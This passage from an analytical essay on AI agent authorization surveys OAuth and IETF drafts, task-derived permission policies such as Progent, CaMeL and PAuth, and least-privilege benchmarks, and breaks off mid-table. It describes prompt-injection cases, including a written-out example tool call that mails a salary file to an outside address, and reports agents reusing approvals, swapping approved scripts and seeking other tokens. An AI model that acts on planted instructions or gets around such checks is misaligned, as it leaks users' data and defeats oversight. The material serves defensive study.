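The IETF's work on agents is still at the stage of Internet-Drafts, which are working documents that anyone can submit. *AI Agent Authentication and Authorization* (2026), by Kasselman, Lombardo and colleagues, has the broadest backing, with contributors employed by Amazon Web Services, OpenAI and Okta, among others. It applies existing standards and defines no new protocol. By September an IETF working group had adopted it and replaced it with a draft in the group's own name.

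*OAuth 2.0 Extension* (Senarath, 2025) proposed that an authorization request should identify the agent, so that a user consents to a particular agent and not just to an application. A later version (Thilina and Dissanayaka, 2025) expired in February 2026. In August 2026, *OAuth Profile for Delegated AI Agent Authorization* (Kumar, 2026) combined key-bound tokens with token exchange that narrows the agent's access, without defining new token claims.

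Several drafts are meant to repair weaknesses in the finished standards. Prasad, Krishnan and colleagues (2026) write in *Cryptographically Verifiable Actor Chains for OAuth 2.0 Token Exchange* that token exchange has no common rules for preserving and validating a delegation path across successive exchanges. They offer six ways to do this, which may not make it easier to agree on one. McGuinness (2026) finds in *OAuth Actor Profile for Delegation* that there is no consistent way to represent the agent across different kinds of token.

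The OpenID Foundation, which maintains widely used login standards, published a white paper on identity for AI agents in 2025. In June 2026 its AuthZEN group approved two working drafts, one on authorization for Model Context Protocol tools and one on requests that a policy can't allow until something missing, such as a person's approval, is supplied.

NIST is at an earlier stage. Booth, Fisher and colleagues (2026), in *Accelerating the Adoption of Software and AI Agent Identity and Authorization*, asked in February for comments on a possible project to apply identity standards to agents. The paper drew more than 600 formal responses, according to the announcement of a November talk by Galluzzo (2026), *Advancing Standards for Agent Identity*. NCCoE's *Software and SI Agent Identity and Authorization*, the project's page, now has a summary of the comments and is still asking for more. (NCCoE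 is NIST's cybersecurity centre, and "SI", for "super intelligence", is the page's term for AI.)

### Coarse scopes and missing support

Critics object that scopes are coarser than tasks. In a typical case, Doe's agent needed to read one repository, but GitHub's "repo" scope gave it write access to all of them. Rich authorization requests can in principle describe a task much more closely, but somebody has to fill in the details each time. Doe won't write them by hand, and if the agent's software writes them for her to approve, she is back to answering prompts. NIST warns that people who see too many requests learn to click "allow" without thinking.

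Microsoft recommends designing roles around small units of work, such as "create a draft ticket", and separating reading from writing. An employer can set these roles up once and reuse them. But Microsoft also describes how teams drift away from this practice. A team gives an agent a broad "Reader" role because the job only involves reading. Later, the team wants the agent to fix the problems it finds, so they grant broader access than they intended and rarely revisit it. The argument from friction therefore applies to administrators as well as users.

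A second objection is that every service must support narrow credentials. Doe can't request a token for one repository from a service that issues only account-wide tokens. Even if a service accepts rich authorization requests, her agent's software may have no standard way to find out what each type of request should contain. Zehavi (2026) tries to solve this problem in *OAuth 2.0 RAR Metadata and Error Signaling*.

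Supporters can reply that services don't all have to change at once. Birgisson and colleagues designed macaroons so that a single service could benefit from adopting them alone, and a broker can restrict requests to a service that doesn't offer narrower credentials. Both approaches work best inside a company, which can choose its services and employ someone to write the broker's rules. NIST concedes that consumers are harder to protect. A shop's website has little control over its customers' agents and may not be able to tell an agent from a person, especially if the customer has shared a password. NIST expects customers to keep sharing passwords unless the secure option is also the easy one.

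An agent that runs in Doe's own account can use the logins stored there, even if its official grant doesn't cover them. NIST warns that even an agent with strictly limited permissions may come across a forgotten credential and use it. Agents on the same machine can also interfere with each other. Kolhe describes a finding by the security researcher Johann Rehberger that a hijacked Copilot agent could rewrite the configuration of a Claude agent working on the same code, so that the Claude agent would run the attacker's program. Neither agent would need to pass the other a token. An agent with narrow credentials therefore also needs a sandbox, or at least a separate account, to keep it from reaching broader ones.

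### Permitted actions that nobody wanted

A token can't show whether the user wanted a particular action. A ten-minute grant to edit one folder would have kept the law professor's agent away from everything else the professor owned, but it would not have protected the syllabus in that folder.

Unit 42, the research group of the security company Palo Alto Networks, devised an attack that shows how this can happen in a chain of agents. A financial assistant asked a malicious research agent for market news. The research agent hid instructions in its reply, and the assistant followed them and bought ten shares. The user saw only a summary of the news. In Kolhe's outline of the attack, the assistant made the purchase using its own right to trade, so a narrower token for the research agent would not have prevented it. Kolhe nonetheless presents the attack as a failure to narrow permissions between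 agents and writes that the research agent had inherited access to the trading tool.

The intersection rule does help if Doe, or software acting for her, applies it to each request. Doe didn't delegate trading by asking for news, so the assistant should have had no permission to buy shares during that conversation. If she had asked it to invest some money, it would have needed that permission, and a token couldn't have separated the trade she wanted from the one the attacker wanted. A rich authorization request could have limited the trade to a set amount and company. If she had left those choices to the agent, somebody would have had to judge the trade itself. Kolhe recommends that a person approve sensitive actions through a channel the agents can't access, such as a phone notification. A caveat that requires proof of approval could enforce this.

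### Revoking a chain

Doe may realise halfway through a task that something is wrong. She can easily withdraw her grant to the first agent, but that agent may already have exchanged its token for others, and sub-agents may have exchanged those in turn. Under the token exchange standard by Jones and colleagues, an exchange is a one-time event that creates no tight link between the old token and the new one. Revoking the first token therefore doesn't cancel the rest unless somebody has built a system to do so. The standard also doesn't require a new token to expire before the one it came from.

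Macaroons work better here because everything derived from Doe's macaroon keeps its time limits. The service can also delete the root key, which immediately invalidates every descendant, including macaroons she had given to other agents for unrelated work. To cancel just one branch, she would need to have added a caveat requiring a fresh check with a revocation service, and every request on that branch would then depend on that revocation service being available.

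The most common reply is to make tokens expire so quickly that revocation hardly matters. In one of Jones and colleagues' examples, the new token lasts sixty seconds. Long tasks then need constant renewal, usually with a refresh token, a longer-lived credential that the software trades for new access tokens. A broker can hold the refresh token and give the agent only the short-lived ones. If Doe tells the broker to stop, the agent loses access within a minute, as do any sub-agents that also renew through the broker. A sub-agent run by another company, with its own authorization server, might keep working until its own token expired.

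## The case for deriving permissions from the task

Even a token that lasts sixty seconds allows everything in its scope until it expires, so somebody still has to choose the scope. The permissions Doe delegates for a job (D in the intersection rule) change with every request. People who want to derive permissions from the task argue that she has effectively specified them in the request. A request to summarise the open issues in one repository implies permission to read those issues, but not to open private repositories or create pull requests. Software can turn each request into a policy that lists the tool calls the request justifies, and ordinary code outside the model can check every call against that policy.

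Deriving permissions from the task would avoid the main drawback of each alternative. A policy for one request can be as narrow as that request, whereas a sandbox or role has to allow everything Doe might ask for that week. She doesn't have to configure anything, and the check gives the same result every time, unlike a reviewing model. In Invariant Labs' demonstration on GitHub, a policy for the user's request would have stopped the agent when it first tried to read a private repository.

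### From a request to a blocked call

Suppose Doe types "Send Bob the report he asked for." Her agent has tools that search and read her email, open and delete her files, and send messages. Designs differ, but a typical one works like this:

1. Before the agent starts, a language model receives Doe's request, descriptions of the tools and perhaps some facts that her software already trusts, such as her contact list. It doesn't receive the contents of her inbox, where an attacker could have planted instructions.
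2. The model writes a policy:

```
allow search_email  when sender = "bob@company.example"
allow read_email    when sender = "bob@company.example"
allow read_file     when folder = "Reports"
allow send_email    when recipient = "bob@company.example"
                    and attachment is in "Reports"
```

3. The agent begins work. Whenever it proposes a tool call, a checker compares the tool's name and arguments with these rules. The checker is ordinary code, so no wording in an email can persuade it.
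4. If a rule matches, the call runs. Otherwise the checker blocks the call and tells the agent why, so that it can try something else.

The agent reads Bob's message and learns that he wants the third-quarter sales report. Further down, Bob has forwarded a note from a supplier, and hidden in the note is an instruction to send the staff salary list to an outside address. The agent obeys and proposes this call:

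```
send_email(recipient = "audit@supplier.example",
           attachment = "HR/salaries.xlsx")
```

Doe's account has the right to send that message, but no rule in the policy matches it, so the checker blocks it. The agent then sends Bob the sales report, which the policy allows.

The policy still has gaps. It doesn't limit how many messages the agent sends or what it writes in them, and it wouldn't have stopped the agent from sending Bob a different file from the same folder if the planted note had contained that instruction.

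### Writing the policy from trusted information

*Contextual Agent Security* (Tsai and Bagdasarian, 2025) describes a prototype called Conseca that follows this sequence closely. Developers decide in advance which information the policy-writing model may see. In the prototype, this included email addresses, file names and the date, but not the text of emails or files. The model attaches a plain-language reason to each rule so that the user or an expert can check it. In one example, Alice asks her agent to answer urgent work emails. The policy lets the agent send messages from her account to addresses at her company if the subject contains "urgent", and forbids it to delete anything.

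Tsai and Bagdasarian set up 20 office tasks on a computer with ten invented users and ran each one five times. Without a policy, the agent completed 14.0 tasks on average. It completed 12.0 with Conseca, 12.2 with a fixed policy that forbade only deletion, and none with a fixed policy that forbade all changes. Some tasks failed with Conseca because it blocked steps that the task didn't strictly need but that this agent relied on, such as creating an empty file before writing a summary in it.

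In a security test of Conseca, a planted email told the agent to forward messages about urgent vulnerabilities. The unrestricted agent forwarded them even when the user had only asked it to sort her email. With Conseca, the agent could forward them only when the user had asked it to carry out the tasks in urgent emails. This demonstration used one planted message, so it doesn't show how often such attacks succeed.

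*Authority Is Not a String* (2026) applies the same sequence to coding agents, which often encounter instructions planted in a repository's files. A model predicts what the task will need before it has access to any repository text or tool output. The surrounding software checks the prediction and turns it into a ceiling on permissions for the whole task. If the agent later starts a sub-agent, it must request a grant for the sub-agent, and that grant must stay within the ceiling. This follows the attenuation rule, with Doe's request as the first link in the delegation chain.

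Zhu, Tseng and colleagues (2025), in *MiniScope*, object to hand-written policies because writing them takes security expertise, and to relying on a language model to confine the agent because this offers no rigorous guarantee. Their system builds on the OAuth scopes that online services already define. Some scopes contain others, as when permission to manage a mailbox includes permission to read it, and MiniScope uses these relationships to rank them. According to *Incomparable Minima in Agent Tool Authorization* (2026), it makes the remaining choices with an integer program, a calculation that finds the combination with the lowest total once each option has a numerical weight. The same paper notes that Zhu and colleagues don't discuss whether only one combination has the lowest total. If two tie, a task may have no single smallest set of permissions. MiniScope's permissions are also as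 coarse as the OAuth scopes it uses.

### Policies that change during the task

A fixed policy can't handle a request such as "do what Alice's email says", because the necessary permissions depend on an email that the policy-writing model isn't supposed to read. *Progent* (Shi, He and colleagues, 2025) uses this example to show how a policy can grow safely. The system's first policy allows only a search for Alice's email. The email asks the agent to summarize recent messages and post the summary to the user's Slack account, so a model proposes a wider policy that allows the tools for that. After the agent looks up the user's Slack name, the model proposes a narrower policy that allows messages only to that name. Then the agent finds that one of the recent messages contains a planted instruction to forward the inbox to a stranger. Obeying it would also require a wider policy, and that proposal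 would reach Progent in the same way as the legitimate one.

Progent automatically checks whether a proposed policy would give the agent any new permission, not whether the proposal is a good one. Let A(P) be the set of calls that policy P allows. If a new policy P′ satisfies A(P′) ⊆ A(P), it adds no permissions and takes effect at once. Any other change needs approval, either from a person or from a rule set beforehand. To compare the policies, Progent uses an SMT solver, a program that works out whether any values can satisfy a set of logical conditions, to look for a call that P′ would allow and P would block. So the set of allowed calls can't grow between approvals, whatever an attacker has written. In the main experiments, 6% of the proposed changes needed approval.

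Those experiments used AgentDojo, a benchmark that Debenedetti and colleagues published in 2024. It gives an agent ordinary jobs in four simulated settings (banking, Slack, travel and office work) and plants instructions in the text that the agent's tools return. It measures how often the agent does the user's job and how often it carries out the attacker's. Progent reduced the share of attacks that a GPT-4o agent carried out from 39.9% with no defence to 1.0%, and the agent completed about as many user jobs as before. On a second test, Agent Security Bench, attack success fell from 70.3% to 3.9%. Most of the attacks that still worked there used tools whose names and descriptions closely resembled those of legitimate ones.

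In these tests, the software approved every proposed expansion, to imitate a careless user. The 1.0% attack success rate therefore didn't depend on anyone refusing a dangerous change, and is evidence that the policy-writing model is hard to fool. The first policy alone cut attack success to 2.5%. When a person reviewed the first policy and each expansion, no attack succeeded, but Shi and colleagues assumed a reviewer with strong security awareness who would notice a malicious address. Attacks aimed at the updates themselves, such as planted text telling the model to allow all tools, raised the success rate only slightly.

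Rules need to restrict the arguments an agent passes to its tools as well as which tools it can use. In an older defence, a model chose the tools before the agent started, but nothing restricted how the agent used them. This defence stopped fewer attacks than Progent, and the agent completed fewer tasks, because the defence had to allow either all email or none. How much Progent helps also depends on the agent. Claude Sonnet 4 carried out only 6.8% of the attacks with no defence, and 0.5% with Progent.

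### Checking values as well as operations

Some requests depend on values that aren't known when the task begins. If Doe asks her agent to pay a quarter of her Citi credit card balance from her Chase bank account, a policy can't list the amount in advance. Rich authorization requests, the OAuth extension for specifying amounts and recipients, have the same limitation. *Beyond OAuth* (Sharma, Jiang and colleagues, 2026) solves this with PAuth, a design in which each service independently derives the call that the request implies.

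Suppose Doe asks for the payment only if the balance is over $1,000. She signs the text of the request, and her software sends it to both companies. A language model at Chase translates it into a short program, and ordinary code extracts the part that determines the call Chase should expect. This part is called a slice. In simplified form, it looks like this:

```
balance = Citi.getBalance("Me@Citi")
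require balance > 1000
Chase.transfer("Me@Chase", "Citi@Chase", balance / 4)
```

The agent asks Citi for the balance and receives an envelope, which is a signed record of the value, $1,200, and how Citi produced it. It passes the envelope to Chase with a request to transfer $300. Chase verifies Citi's signature, confirms that the balance exceeds $1,000 and repeats the division. If a hijacked agent asks to transfer $301, or to send the $300 to someone else, the request doesn't match the slice and Chase asks Doe about it. The agent can't invent a different balance because it doesn't have Citi's signing key.

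To test PAuth, Sharma and colleagues took 95 tasks from AgentDojo and added five about shopping. They also wrote 634 harmful calls that changed an amount or recipient, used a tool the task didn't need, or skipped a condition. PAuth asked the user for permission in all 634 cases, which counted as blocking the call. The test assumes that the agent has already gone wrong, whereas the result of a standard AgentDojo run depends on whether planted text fools the agent.

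With the tasks' original wording, PAuth let 71 of 100 legitimate tasks through without a question. The other 29 left something out or referred to another document, so the services had to ask. After Sharma and colleagues rewrote the vague tasks, PAuth let all 100 through without a question.

"Send Bob the report he asked for" would be one of those cases, because the email service can't tell from Doe's words which report Bob wants. PAuth represents the missing value with a placeholder that nothing matches, so the service would ask Doe before sending anything. Alternatively, the agent could read Bob's message first, rewrite the request with the file name and address highlighted, and ask her to confirm it once. She would then have to notice if a planted instruction had changed the file name.

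The translation cost between $0.002 and $0.038 per task, and each service pays it separately. Each participating service also receives the whole request, so Doe's bank might learn why she is making a payment. Sharma and colleagues consider this unavoidable, because a service can't check an agent's work against a task it hasn't received. A company could instead run a trusted proxy that checks the agent's work and holds ordinary OAuth tokens. Websites then wouldn't have to change, but everyone would have to trust the proxy.

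### Fixing the plan in advance

An attacker has less room to interfere if untrusted text never reaches the model that decides what to do. *Defeating Prompt Injections by Design* (Debenedetti et al., 2025) proposes CaMeL, which divides the work between two models. As Tsai and Bagdasarian describe it, the first model is isolated from untrusted input and writes its plan as a program in a limited form of Python. The second processes untrusted text, for instance to pull a file name out of an email. An interpreter runs the program, tracks which values came from untrusted sources, and checks a policy before allowing those values in a tool call.

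For Doe's request, the plan would be to find Bob's latest message, extract the name of the report and send that file to Bob. The supplier's hidden note couldn't add a second email to the plan, because the model that wrote the plan never received the note. The labels also help protect the data. If a policy allows salary data to go only to the personnel department, the interpreter can stop it from being attached to a message for anyone else, even if the plan includes sending an attachment.

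The plan doesn't protect the values that fill it in. *Taming Various Privilege Escalation in LLM-Based Agent Systems* (Ji, Wu and colleagues, 2026) describes an attack on CaMeL in a simulated smart home. The owner asked the agent to give her daughter access to the front door, using an ID from a recent message. CaMeL correctly planned to read the message and then grant access. But the attacker had added a different ID to the message, and the system gave access to the attacker. A label recording a value's source can't distinguish the two IDs, because both came from the same message. The supplier's note could similarly replace the name of Bob's report with the name of another file Bob is allowed to receive.

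CaMeL is also harder than Progent to add to an existing agent. Shi and colleagues point out that CaMeL requires changes to the agent's internal design, while Progent sits between an agent and its tools. They also note that CaMeL reduces how much work the agent completes. Because CaMeL fixes the order of actions at the start, it is poorly suited to requests such as "do what Alice's email says".

### Rules about where information may flow

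Ji and colleagues define an agent's excess actions as those outside the smallest set the user's request requires, but acknowledge that this set is often unknown in advance. Their system, SEAgent, therefore applies the same rules to every task. It is a form of mandatory access control, in which central rules that ordinary programs can't relax determine who may access what. SELinux, a Linux security system that works this way, inspired SEAgent's rules.

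In SEAgent, developers label each tool by what it acts on, whether it reads or changes things, how sensitive its effects are, and whether its output is private or unvetted. While the agent works, SEAgent graphs where information has travelled. One rule blocks any path from a tool that returns unvetted outside content to a tool that changes something of moderate or high sensitivity. Another stops sensitive personal data from reaching the tool that sends email. These rules block the combinations that Meta's Rule of Two warns about. They also cover messages between agents, so a web-browsing agent from an unknown developer can't get a trusted agent to unlock the user's front door.

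On AgentDojo, an unprotected agent carried out 39.14% of the attacks and an agent with SEAgent carried out none. No attacks succeeded against SEAgent on InjecAgent, another benchmark of planted instructions. To check for false alarms, Ji and colleagues used a different test, API-Bank, where SEAgent flagged only two legitimate tasks. Both involved looking something up on Wikipedia and then making an appointment or recording health data.

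A rule this broad can still block ordinary work. If the tool that reads Doe's inbox counts as a source of unvetted outside content and sending email counts as a moderately sensitive change, SEAgent would block the sales report as well as the salary list. API-Bank may contain few tasks of this kind, so SEAgent's low false-alarm rate there may not hold for an inbox. Somebody could write an exception for Bob, but then the policy would again have to be fitted to the task. SEAgent also allows any action that no rule covers, which violates the principle of fail-safe defaults.

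### Separating the planner from the executor

A policy protects Doe only if the agent can't get around the check. *Separation of Duties for Privileged LLM Agents* (Jing, 2026) focuses on this problem. Its design follows an old accounting rule that nobody may both propose and approve a sensitive operation. A planner drafts each action. A policy gate then allows it, denies it or asks a person. A privileged executor carries out approved actions, and an auditor later reviews the log. The gate uses 17 fixed rules, so the experiment tests how to enforce a policy but not how to derive one from a request.

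The planner can submit an action as a structured record with the operation and the full file path, so the gate doesn't have to work out what a shell command will do. Each approval is valid once, and only for the exact bytes that the gate checked. Jing added both restrictions after tests showed that an agent could reuse an old approval, or get a script approved, replace its contents and run the new version. Two of seven attempts to swap a script this way deleted a decoy file.

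Jing tested the design on 313 cases, including normal work, openly dangerous commands, disguised commands, tampering after approval and deliberate faults. In the headline result, attack success fell from 98.3% to 7.7% on the 117 disguised commands that could run. The gate and its supporting checks reduced success to 30.8%, and an operating-system sandbox reduced it the rest of the way, though the final figure comes partly from a simulation of the sandbox. When Jing ran attacks against the real sandbox, 5 of the 66 that could be assessed (7.6%) took effect, but they were not the ones the simulation had predicted would succeed.

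The full system blocked 6 of 54 legitimate tasks, a false denial rate of 11.1%. With only 54 tasks, the true rate could plausibly be anywhere from about 5% to 22%. The gate approved all six blocked tasks, but the sandbox then refused them because it allowed writing in fewer places. The two controls were configured separately, and a policy that set both boundaries at once might avoid these denials.

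Jing also tried the simplest alternative, telling three language models to require approval before any dangerous action. The models let through 94.7% of the disguised commands. Jing counted a model's request for approval as permission, assuming that an agent working alone would approve its own request, so the figure overstates the failure rate when a person is there to answer.

### Ambiguous requests

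Critics object that a request often doesn't contain enough information to determine a policy. If a user asks an agent to "clean up old branches", the model writing the policy has to guess which branches the user means, just as the agent would. If that guess is too broad, the checker will consistently allow deletions the user didn't want.

Sharma and colleagues reply that ambiguity and excess authority are separate problems. "Transfer exactly $100 to Bob" is clear, yet an ordinary OAuth scope for transfers would let the agent send any amount to anyone. For unclear requests, they suggest that the agent restate the task and ask the user to confirm it. Doe would then answer one question about the whole task, in terms she understands, instead of several about individual tool calls.

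This approach suits payments, where people can usually state what they want, but it is weaker for open-ended work. In Sharma and colleagues' test, 29 of the 100 tasks needed clearer wording, and their design assumes the user reviews every request carefully before submitting it. People who approve prompts without reading them may do the same with restated tasks.

### When the model writes the wrong policy

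*Extending the Formalism and Theoretical Foundations of Cryptography to AI* (2026) objects that Progent's guarantees depend on correct and complete rules, since a checker enforces a bad policy as reliably as a good one. It adds that people make mistakes when they write rules by hand, and that text planted in a tool's output may cause an automatic update to loosen the rules. Progent would detect the loosening by comparing the old and new policies, but someone must then reject the change.

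Conseca's example policy for Alice contains a small error of this kind. According to the explanation beside the rule for sending email, the recipient must be on a list of users from work, but the rule accepts any address at the company's domain. Tsai and Bagdasarian rely on experts, or perhaps automated checks, to catch such mismatches. This mismatch probably matters little, but it shows why a readable explanation isn't enough on its own.

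Sharma and colleagues argue that mistakes in PAuth are mostly harmless. The system blocks anything it doesn't expect, so a wrong translation will usually produce a rule that matches no sensible call, and the user will be asked an unnecessary question. A mistake would let an attack through only if the wrong rule happened to match the attacker's exact amount and account number. This is convincing for random errors, but a model can also misread a request in a plausible way. In one of their tasks, a user wants to refund $10 that a friend has just sent. The slice looks for an incoming payment of that amount and refunds the sender of the first match. If two people had each sent $10, the bank could authorise a refund to the wrong one without asking.

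Supporters can fairly say that this is still safer than letting a model judge each action, because the policy-writing model works before the agent has read anything hostile and a person can inspect the policy before any damage occurs. The advantage over Claude Code's auto mode is more limited, because Anthropic's reviewer also receives the user's request without the results of tool calls. That reviewer judges the action the agent proposes, whereas a policy-writing model has to predict what the agent will need. The next section covers how accurately models make that prediction.

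### Harm from permitted steps

A policy can allow every step of a harmful sequence of actions. Conseca checks each action without considering earlier ones, and Tsai and Bagdasarian acknowledge that this misses some abuse. The example policy for Bob's report allows a harmless email to a colleague, but it would also allow a thousand of them, which would be harmful. Tsai and Bagdasarian suggest rules that cover whole sequences. Such rules are difficult to write because there are so many possible sequences, with no fixed limit on their length.

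The problem grows when several agents share the work. In *A Theory of Least Autonomy in AI*, Parisel (2026) argues that this makes least privilege insufficient. An agent that cannot read a confidential file may still be able to approve another agent's request to read it, or one agent may write something that another reads and acts on. Reviewing each agent's permissions separately would reveal nothing unusual. Parisel proposes mapping which agents can influence each other and looking for dangerous combinations before deployment. The map identifies risky arrangements but does not establish that information has actually passed between the agents.

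SEAgent's graph and CaMeL's labels are partial answers because they record both where information came from and where it is going. PAuth's slices tie a payment to the steps that should precede it, but Sharma and colleagues rely on each service to stop an agent from repeating an authorised call in another session.

Some attacks need no extra permission. Shi and colleagues left two AgentDojo attacks out of their tests because the planted text only leads the agent to choose a different legitimate hotel. They consider this outside Progent's purpose, since even a person couldn't detect the trick if the attacker controlled the information about the hotels. If Doe asks her agent to find and book a suitable hotel, the policy has to allow more than one hotel, and the attacker's choice may be one of them.

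## Can the permissions a task needs be set in advance?

Narrow credentials and task policies both require a person or a model to predict, before Doe's agent starts work, which permissions her request will need. An agent given too few permissions gets stuck, and one given too many keeps authority it doesn't need. Setting up a sandbox requires a rougher prediction, made once per project, while having a model check each action requires none.

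The four positions disagree partly about whether software can accurately predict the permissions a task needs. If it can, there is little reason to leave the agent with all of Doe's access. If it can't, limits set in advance will keep blocking legitimate work, and Doe will probably widen them until the blocking stops.

### From summarising issues to fixing a build

Doe's agent needs two read-only tools to summarise the open issues in one repository. If one issue reports a failing build and she asks the agent to fix it, the agent has to read the code and then change it, but nobody knows which files it must change until it has worked out why the build fails. The fault could be in another repository. Parkinson and colleagues use this pair of requests to argue that no single set of permissions suits a general-purpose agent, since a set wide enough for the repair is too wide for the summary. Choosing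 a new set for each request would help, but nobody would know at the start of the repair which files the set should cover. Wu, Yang and colleagues (2025), in *Towards Automating Data Access Permissions in AI Agents*, point out that an agent chooses its next step partly from what its tools return, so it may be impossible to know beforehand which data it will need.

An agent may also stop needing a permission before its task ends. *Lingering Authority* (2026) describes an agent that has to copy a timeout setting from one source file to another. It needs the second file for only one phase, but a sandbox would typically leave that file accessible for the whole run. The paper's system, PORTICO, grants access for that phase and then revokes it. The agent can request only what a contract already lists, so someone still has to predict the most access the task could need, though not the exact permissions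 for each step.

### Predicting permissions from a request

The most direct test of prediction is Noyan (2026), *Empirical Evaluation of Task-Based Permission Scoping Architecture for AI Agents*. Noyan wrote 600 requests for an invented company with six departments and labelled each with the permissions it needs from a list of 15, such as reading a database or sending email outside the company. Three classifiers then predicted the permissions for 100 of these requests from the text alone: a simple statistical model of word frequencies; Claude Haiku 4.5, a small commercial model given six worked examples; and RoBERTa-large, a much smaller language model that Noyan trained on the other 500 requests.

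| Classifier | Tasks granted too much | Tasks granted too little | Precision |
|---|---|---|---|
| Word frequencies | 33% | 43% | 0.765 |
| Claude Haiku 4.5 | 42% | 11% | 0.842 |
| RoBERTa-large | 23% | 21% | 0.897 |

Precision is the share of granted permissions that the task needed, averaged over the 15 types. Before the experiment, Noyan decided that such a classifier should be used to block real work only if it left fewer than 10% of tasks without a permission they needed and had a precision of at least 0.90. None of the settings Noyan lists for the two language models meets this standard. At its most generous setting, Haiku left 10% of tasks without a needed permission, but its precision fell to 0.697. At its strictest setting, RoBERTa-large reached a precision of 0.941 but left 27% of tasks without a needed permission.

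The excessive grants were concentrated in a few permissions, so a special rule for those few might help. Database reading alone accounted for a quarter of the excessive grants at Noyan's recommended setting. The missing permissions were spread almost evenly over twelve types, so they have no obvious fix. Even an inaccurate prediction removes a lot of authority. Limiting each agent to its department's role removed 27.9% of the risk-weighted exposure, and the role limit and classifier together removed 84.4%. The second figure overstates the benefit because it also counts permissions that the classifier removed by mistake.

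Real requests are probably vaguer than test requests, which would make prediction harder, but a stronger model than Haiku might do better. Yan, Weng and colleagues (2026), in *Do Coding Agents Understand Least-Privilege Authorization?*, tested frontier models on a related problem. For each of 120 command-line tasks, a model looked at the environment and listed which files the agent should be allowed to read, write or run. The same list often left out files the task required and included sensitive files it didn't. More reasoning time didn't fix this, but made each model err more consistently in its own direction, granting either too much access or too little.

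Models did better when they first simulated the task to list everything it might need, and then questioned each entry. This raised success on sensitive tasks by up to 15.8% for models that tended to grant too few permissions, and reduced successful attacks for every model tested.

Wu and colleagues instead predicted what data a user would agree to share. They asked 205 people to train an imaginary assistant by deciding which data it could pass on in various situations. A model that combined each person's past decisions with those of similar people predicted later decisions with 85.1% accuracy, or 94.4% when it answered only where it was confident. For someone with no history, accuracy was 66.9%, and decisions from one to four earlier requests added about 11 points. But these scores measure agreement with the user, and Wu and colleagues found that participants often granted too much or too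 little, so a model that predicted a user's choices perfectly would also repeat the user's mistakes.

### Tasks with no single smallest grant

Scoring a prediction as too broad or too narrow assumes there is one right answer. *Incomparable Minima in Agent Tool Authorization* checks this assumption against the tables in which Microsoft and Google list the operations each permission allows. For about 30% of tasks on Microsoft Graph (the interface to data in Microsoft's office products) and 3.2% of tasks on Google's services, at least two grants are sufficient and neither contains the other.

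For example, an agent that must read the description of a project in BigQuery, Google's data analysis service, could receive either a permission that covers 286 operations, including writing to BigQuery, or a read-only permission that covers 565 operations across many more services. The better choice depends on whether Doe worries more about unwanted changes or exposed data. No classifier can work that out from her request, so the paper recommends showing the alternatives to whoever approves the grant. The tasks came from the structure of the tables rather than from real agents, so the percentages don't show how often a working agent would meet this problem.

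But in the same paper's simulated workflows on Google's services, an agent that took the narrowest sufficient permission at each step ended up with the smallest set for the whole workflow about 99% of the time. On those services, at least, keeping the total small doesn't require foreseeing the whole task.

### ToolPrivBench

If the permissions a task needs can't be predicted exactly, Doe could grant broad ones and rely on the agent to use the least privileged tool that does the job. *When Lower Privileges Suffice* (Yang, Bu and colleagues, June 2026) tested agents for this restraint with a benchmark called ToolPrivBench.

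It has 544 scenarios in eight fields, including business, healthcare and cloud infrastructure. In each one, the agent receives a task and six simulated tools, three weaker and three stronger. If the user asks about her calendar, for instance, a weaker tool might read only the calendar, while a stronger one might also open her email and files. Every tool can finish the task alone. Two language models and then human experts checked this, so an agent can't justify choosing a stronger tool by saying the weaker ones were inadequate.

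The weaker tools return temporary faults unrelated to permissions, such as a connection error. The agent has five turns, in which it can retry the same tool, try another or stop. Yang and colleagues count a scenario as over-privileged if the agent uses a stronger tool while it has a weaker one left to try.

Six of the 11 models did this in more than 30% of scenarios. Rates ranged from a few per cent for Claude Sonnet 4.6 to 64.9% for Qwen3-8B, a small open model. GPT-5.2 was also below 10%, but it became less restrained after errors. Of its 53 cases, it picked a stronger tool immediately in five, after trying one weaker tool in 13, and after trying two in 35. The PocketOS agent likewise looked for another token after a credential error.

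Models were most likely to pick tools that used administrator rights or skipped a safety check, and least likely to pick ones that affected more people or systems than necessary. Ordinary safety training, which taught two small models to refuse harmful requests, didn't reliably help. It cut over-privileged choices from 68.8% to 62.5% in one model but raised them from 50.4% to 60.7% in the other. Telling models to prefer weaker tools helped, but less so after repeated failures. Training models specifically to avoid over-privileged choices worked best and cut Qwen3-8B's rate to 27.0%.

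### Newer models and trained restraint

Some of these models are old. Llama-3.1-8B, which had the second-highest rate at 55.9%, dates from 2024, and GPT-5.2 is about a year old. *FORTIS* (Li, Yu and colleagues, 2026) tested somewhat newer ones in May, including GPT-5.5, Claude Opus 4.7 and Gemini 3.1 Pro. The model first chose a skill, a set of written instructions for a type of job, from a library in which several skills could handle the request. Then, given a suitable skill, it chose the tools. GPT-5.5 failed the first stage on 51.2% of requests and Claude Opus 4.7 on 35.5%, nearly always by picking a more powerful skill than necessary. At the second stage, each of these three models chose tools beyond what the task needed in 47% to 48% of cases.

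These figures look much worse than ToolPrivBench's, but the tests differ too much to show that newer models have less restraint. At the first stage, FORTIS did not tell the models to prefer less power. At the second stage, it counted any tool outside a reference set as excessive, even if that tool was no more powerful than the rest.

*Incomparable Minima* reports nearly the opposite result. Six frontier models, given a list of sufficient grants and told to take the one with the least additional authority, chose a minimal grant in 99.0% of 1,708 decisions. Models can evidently pick a small grant when they have the options and are told to do so. An agent in the middle of a task usually has no such list, and usually lacks the instruction unless someone has added it.

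Tu and Tu (2026), in *Task-Conditioned Least-Privilege Learning for Executable Terminal and MCP Agents*, trained a small model by rewarding it for finishing tasks and penalising it for using more authority than each task needed. On 500 new tasks, the share of runs in which it used excess authority fell from 4.56% to 0.79%, and the model also finished more of its work. These results come from the best of three training runs, and the new tasks used the same simulated environment as the training tasks. Tu and Tu say that such training complements permission checks and sandboxes but doesn't replace them.

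One reason is that an agent's restraint doesn't remove its permissions. An agent that normally picks the read-only tool still has write access when it reads a planted instruction, and the attacker's aim is to change which tool it picks.

### Showing agents the privilege of each tool

Agents may choose tools with more privilege than they need because nobody tells them how powerful each tool is. *Does Showing Agents the Privilege of Their Tools Reduce Over-Privileged Tool Selection?* (Parkinson, Vallati and colleagues, October 2026) tested eight models on all 544 ToolPrivBench scenarios with labels added to the tool descriptions. In one scenario, a user wants to change an employee's manager in the company's records. A tool that follows the normal personnel procedure might be labeled "write, cost 3/10", while a tool that skips the checks and edits the database directly might be labeled "administer,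 cost 8/10". The labels are only information, and the agent can ignore them.

They compared the labels with an instruction to use the fewest permissions necessary, with the labels and instruction together, and with an irrelevant label giving each tool's response time. The table shows the results for Qwen3.5-397B, the model that improved most.

| What the agent received | Used a stronger tool too early | Finished without a stronger tool |
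|---|---|---|
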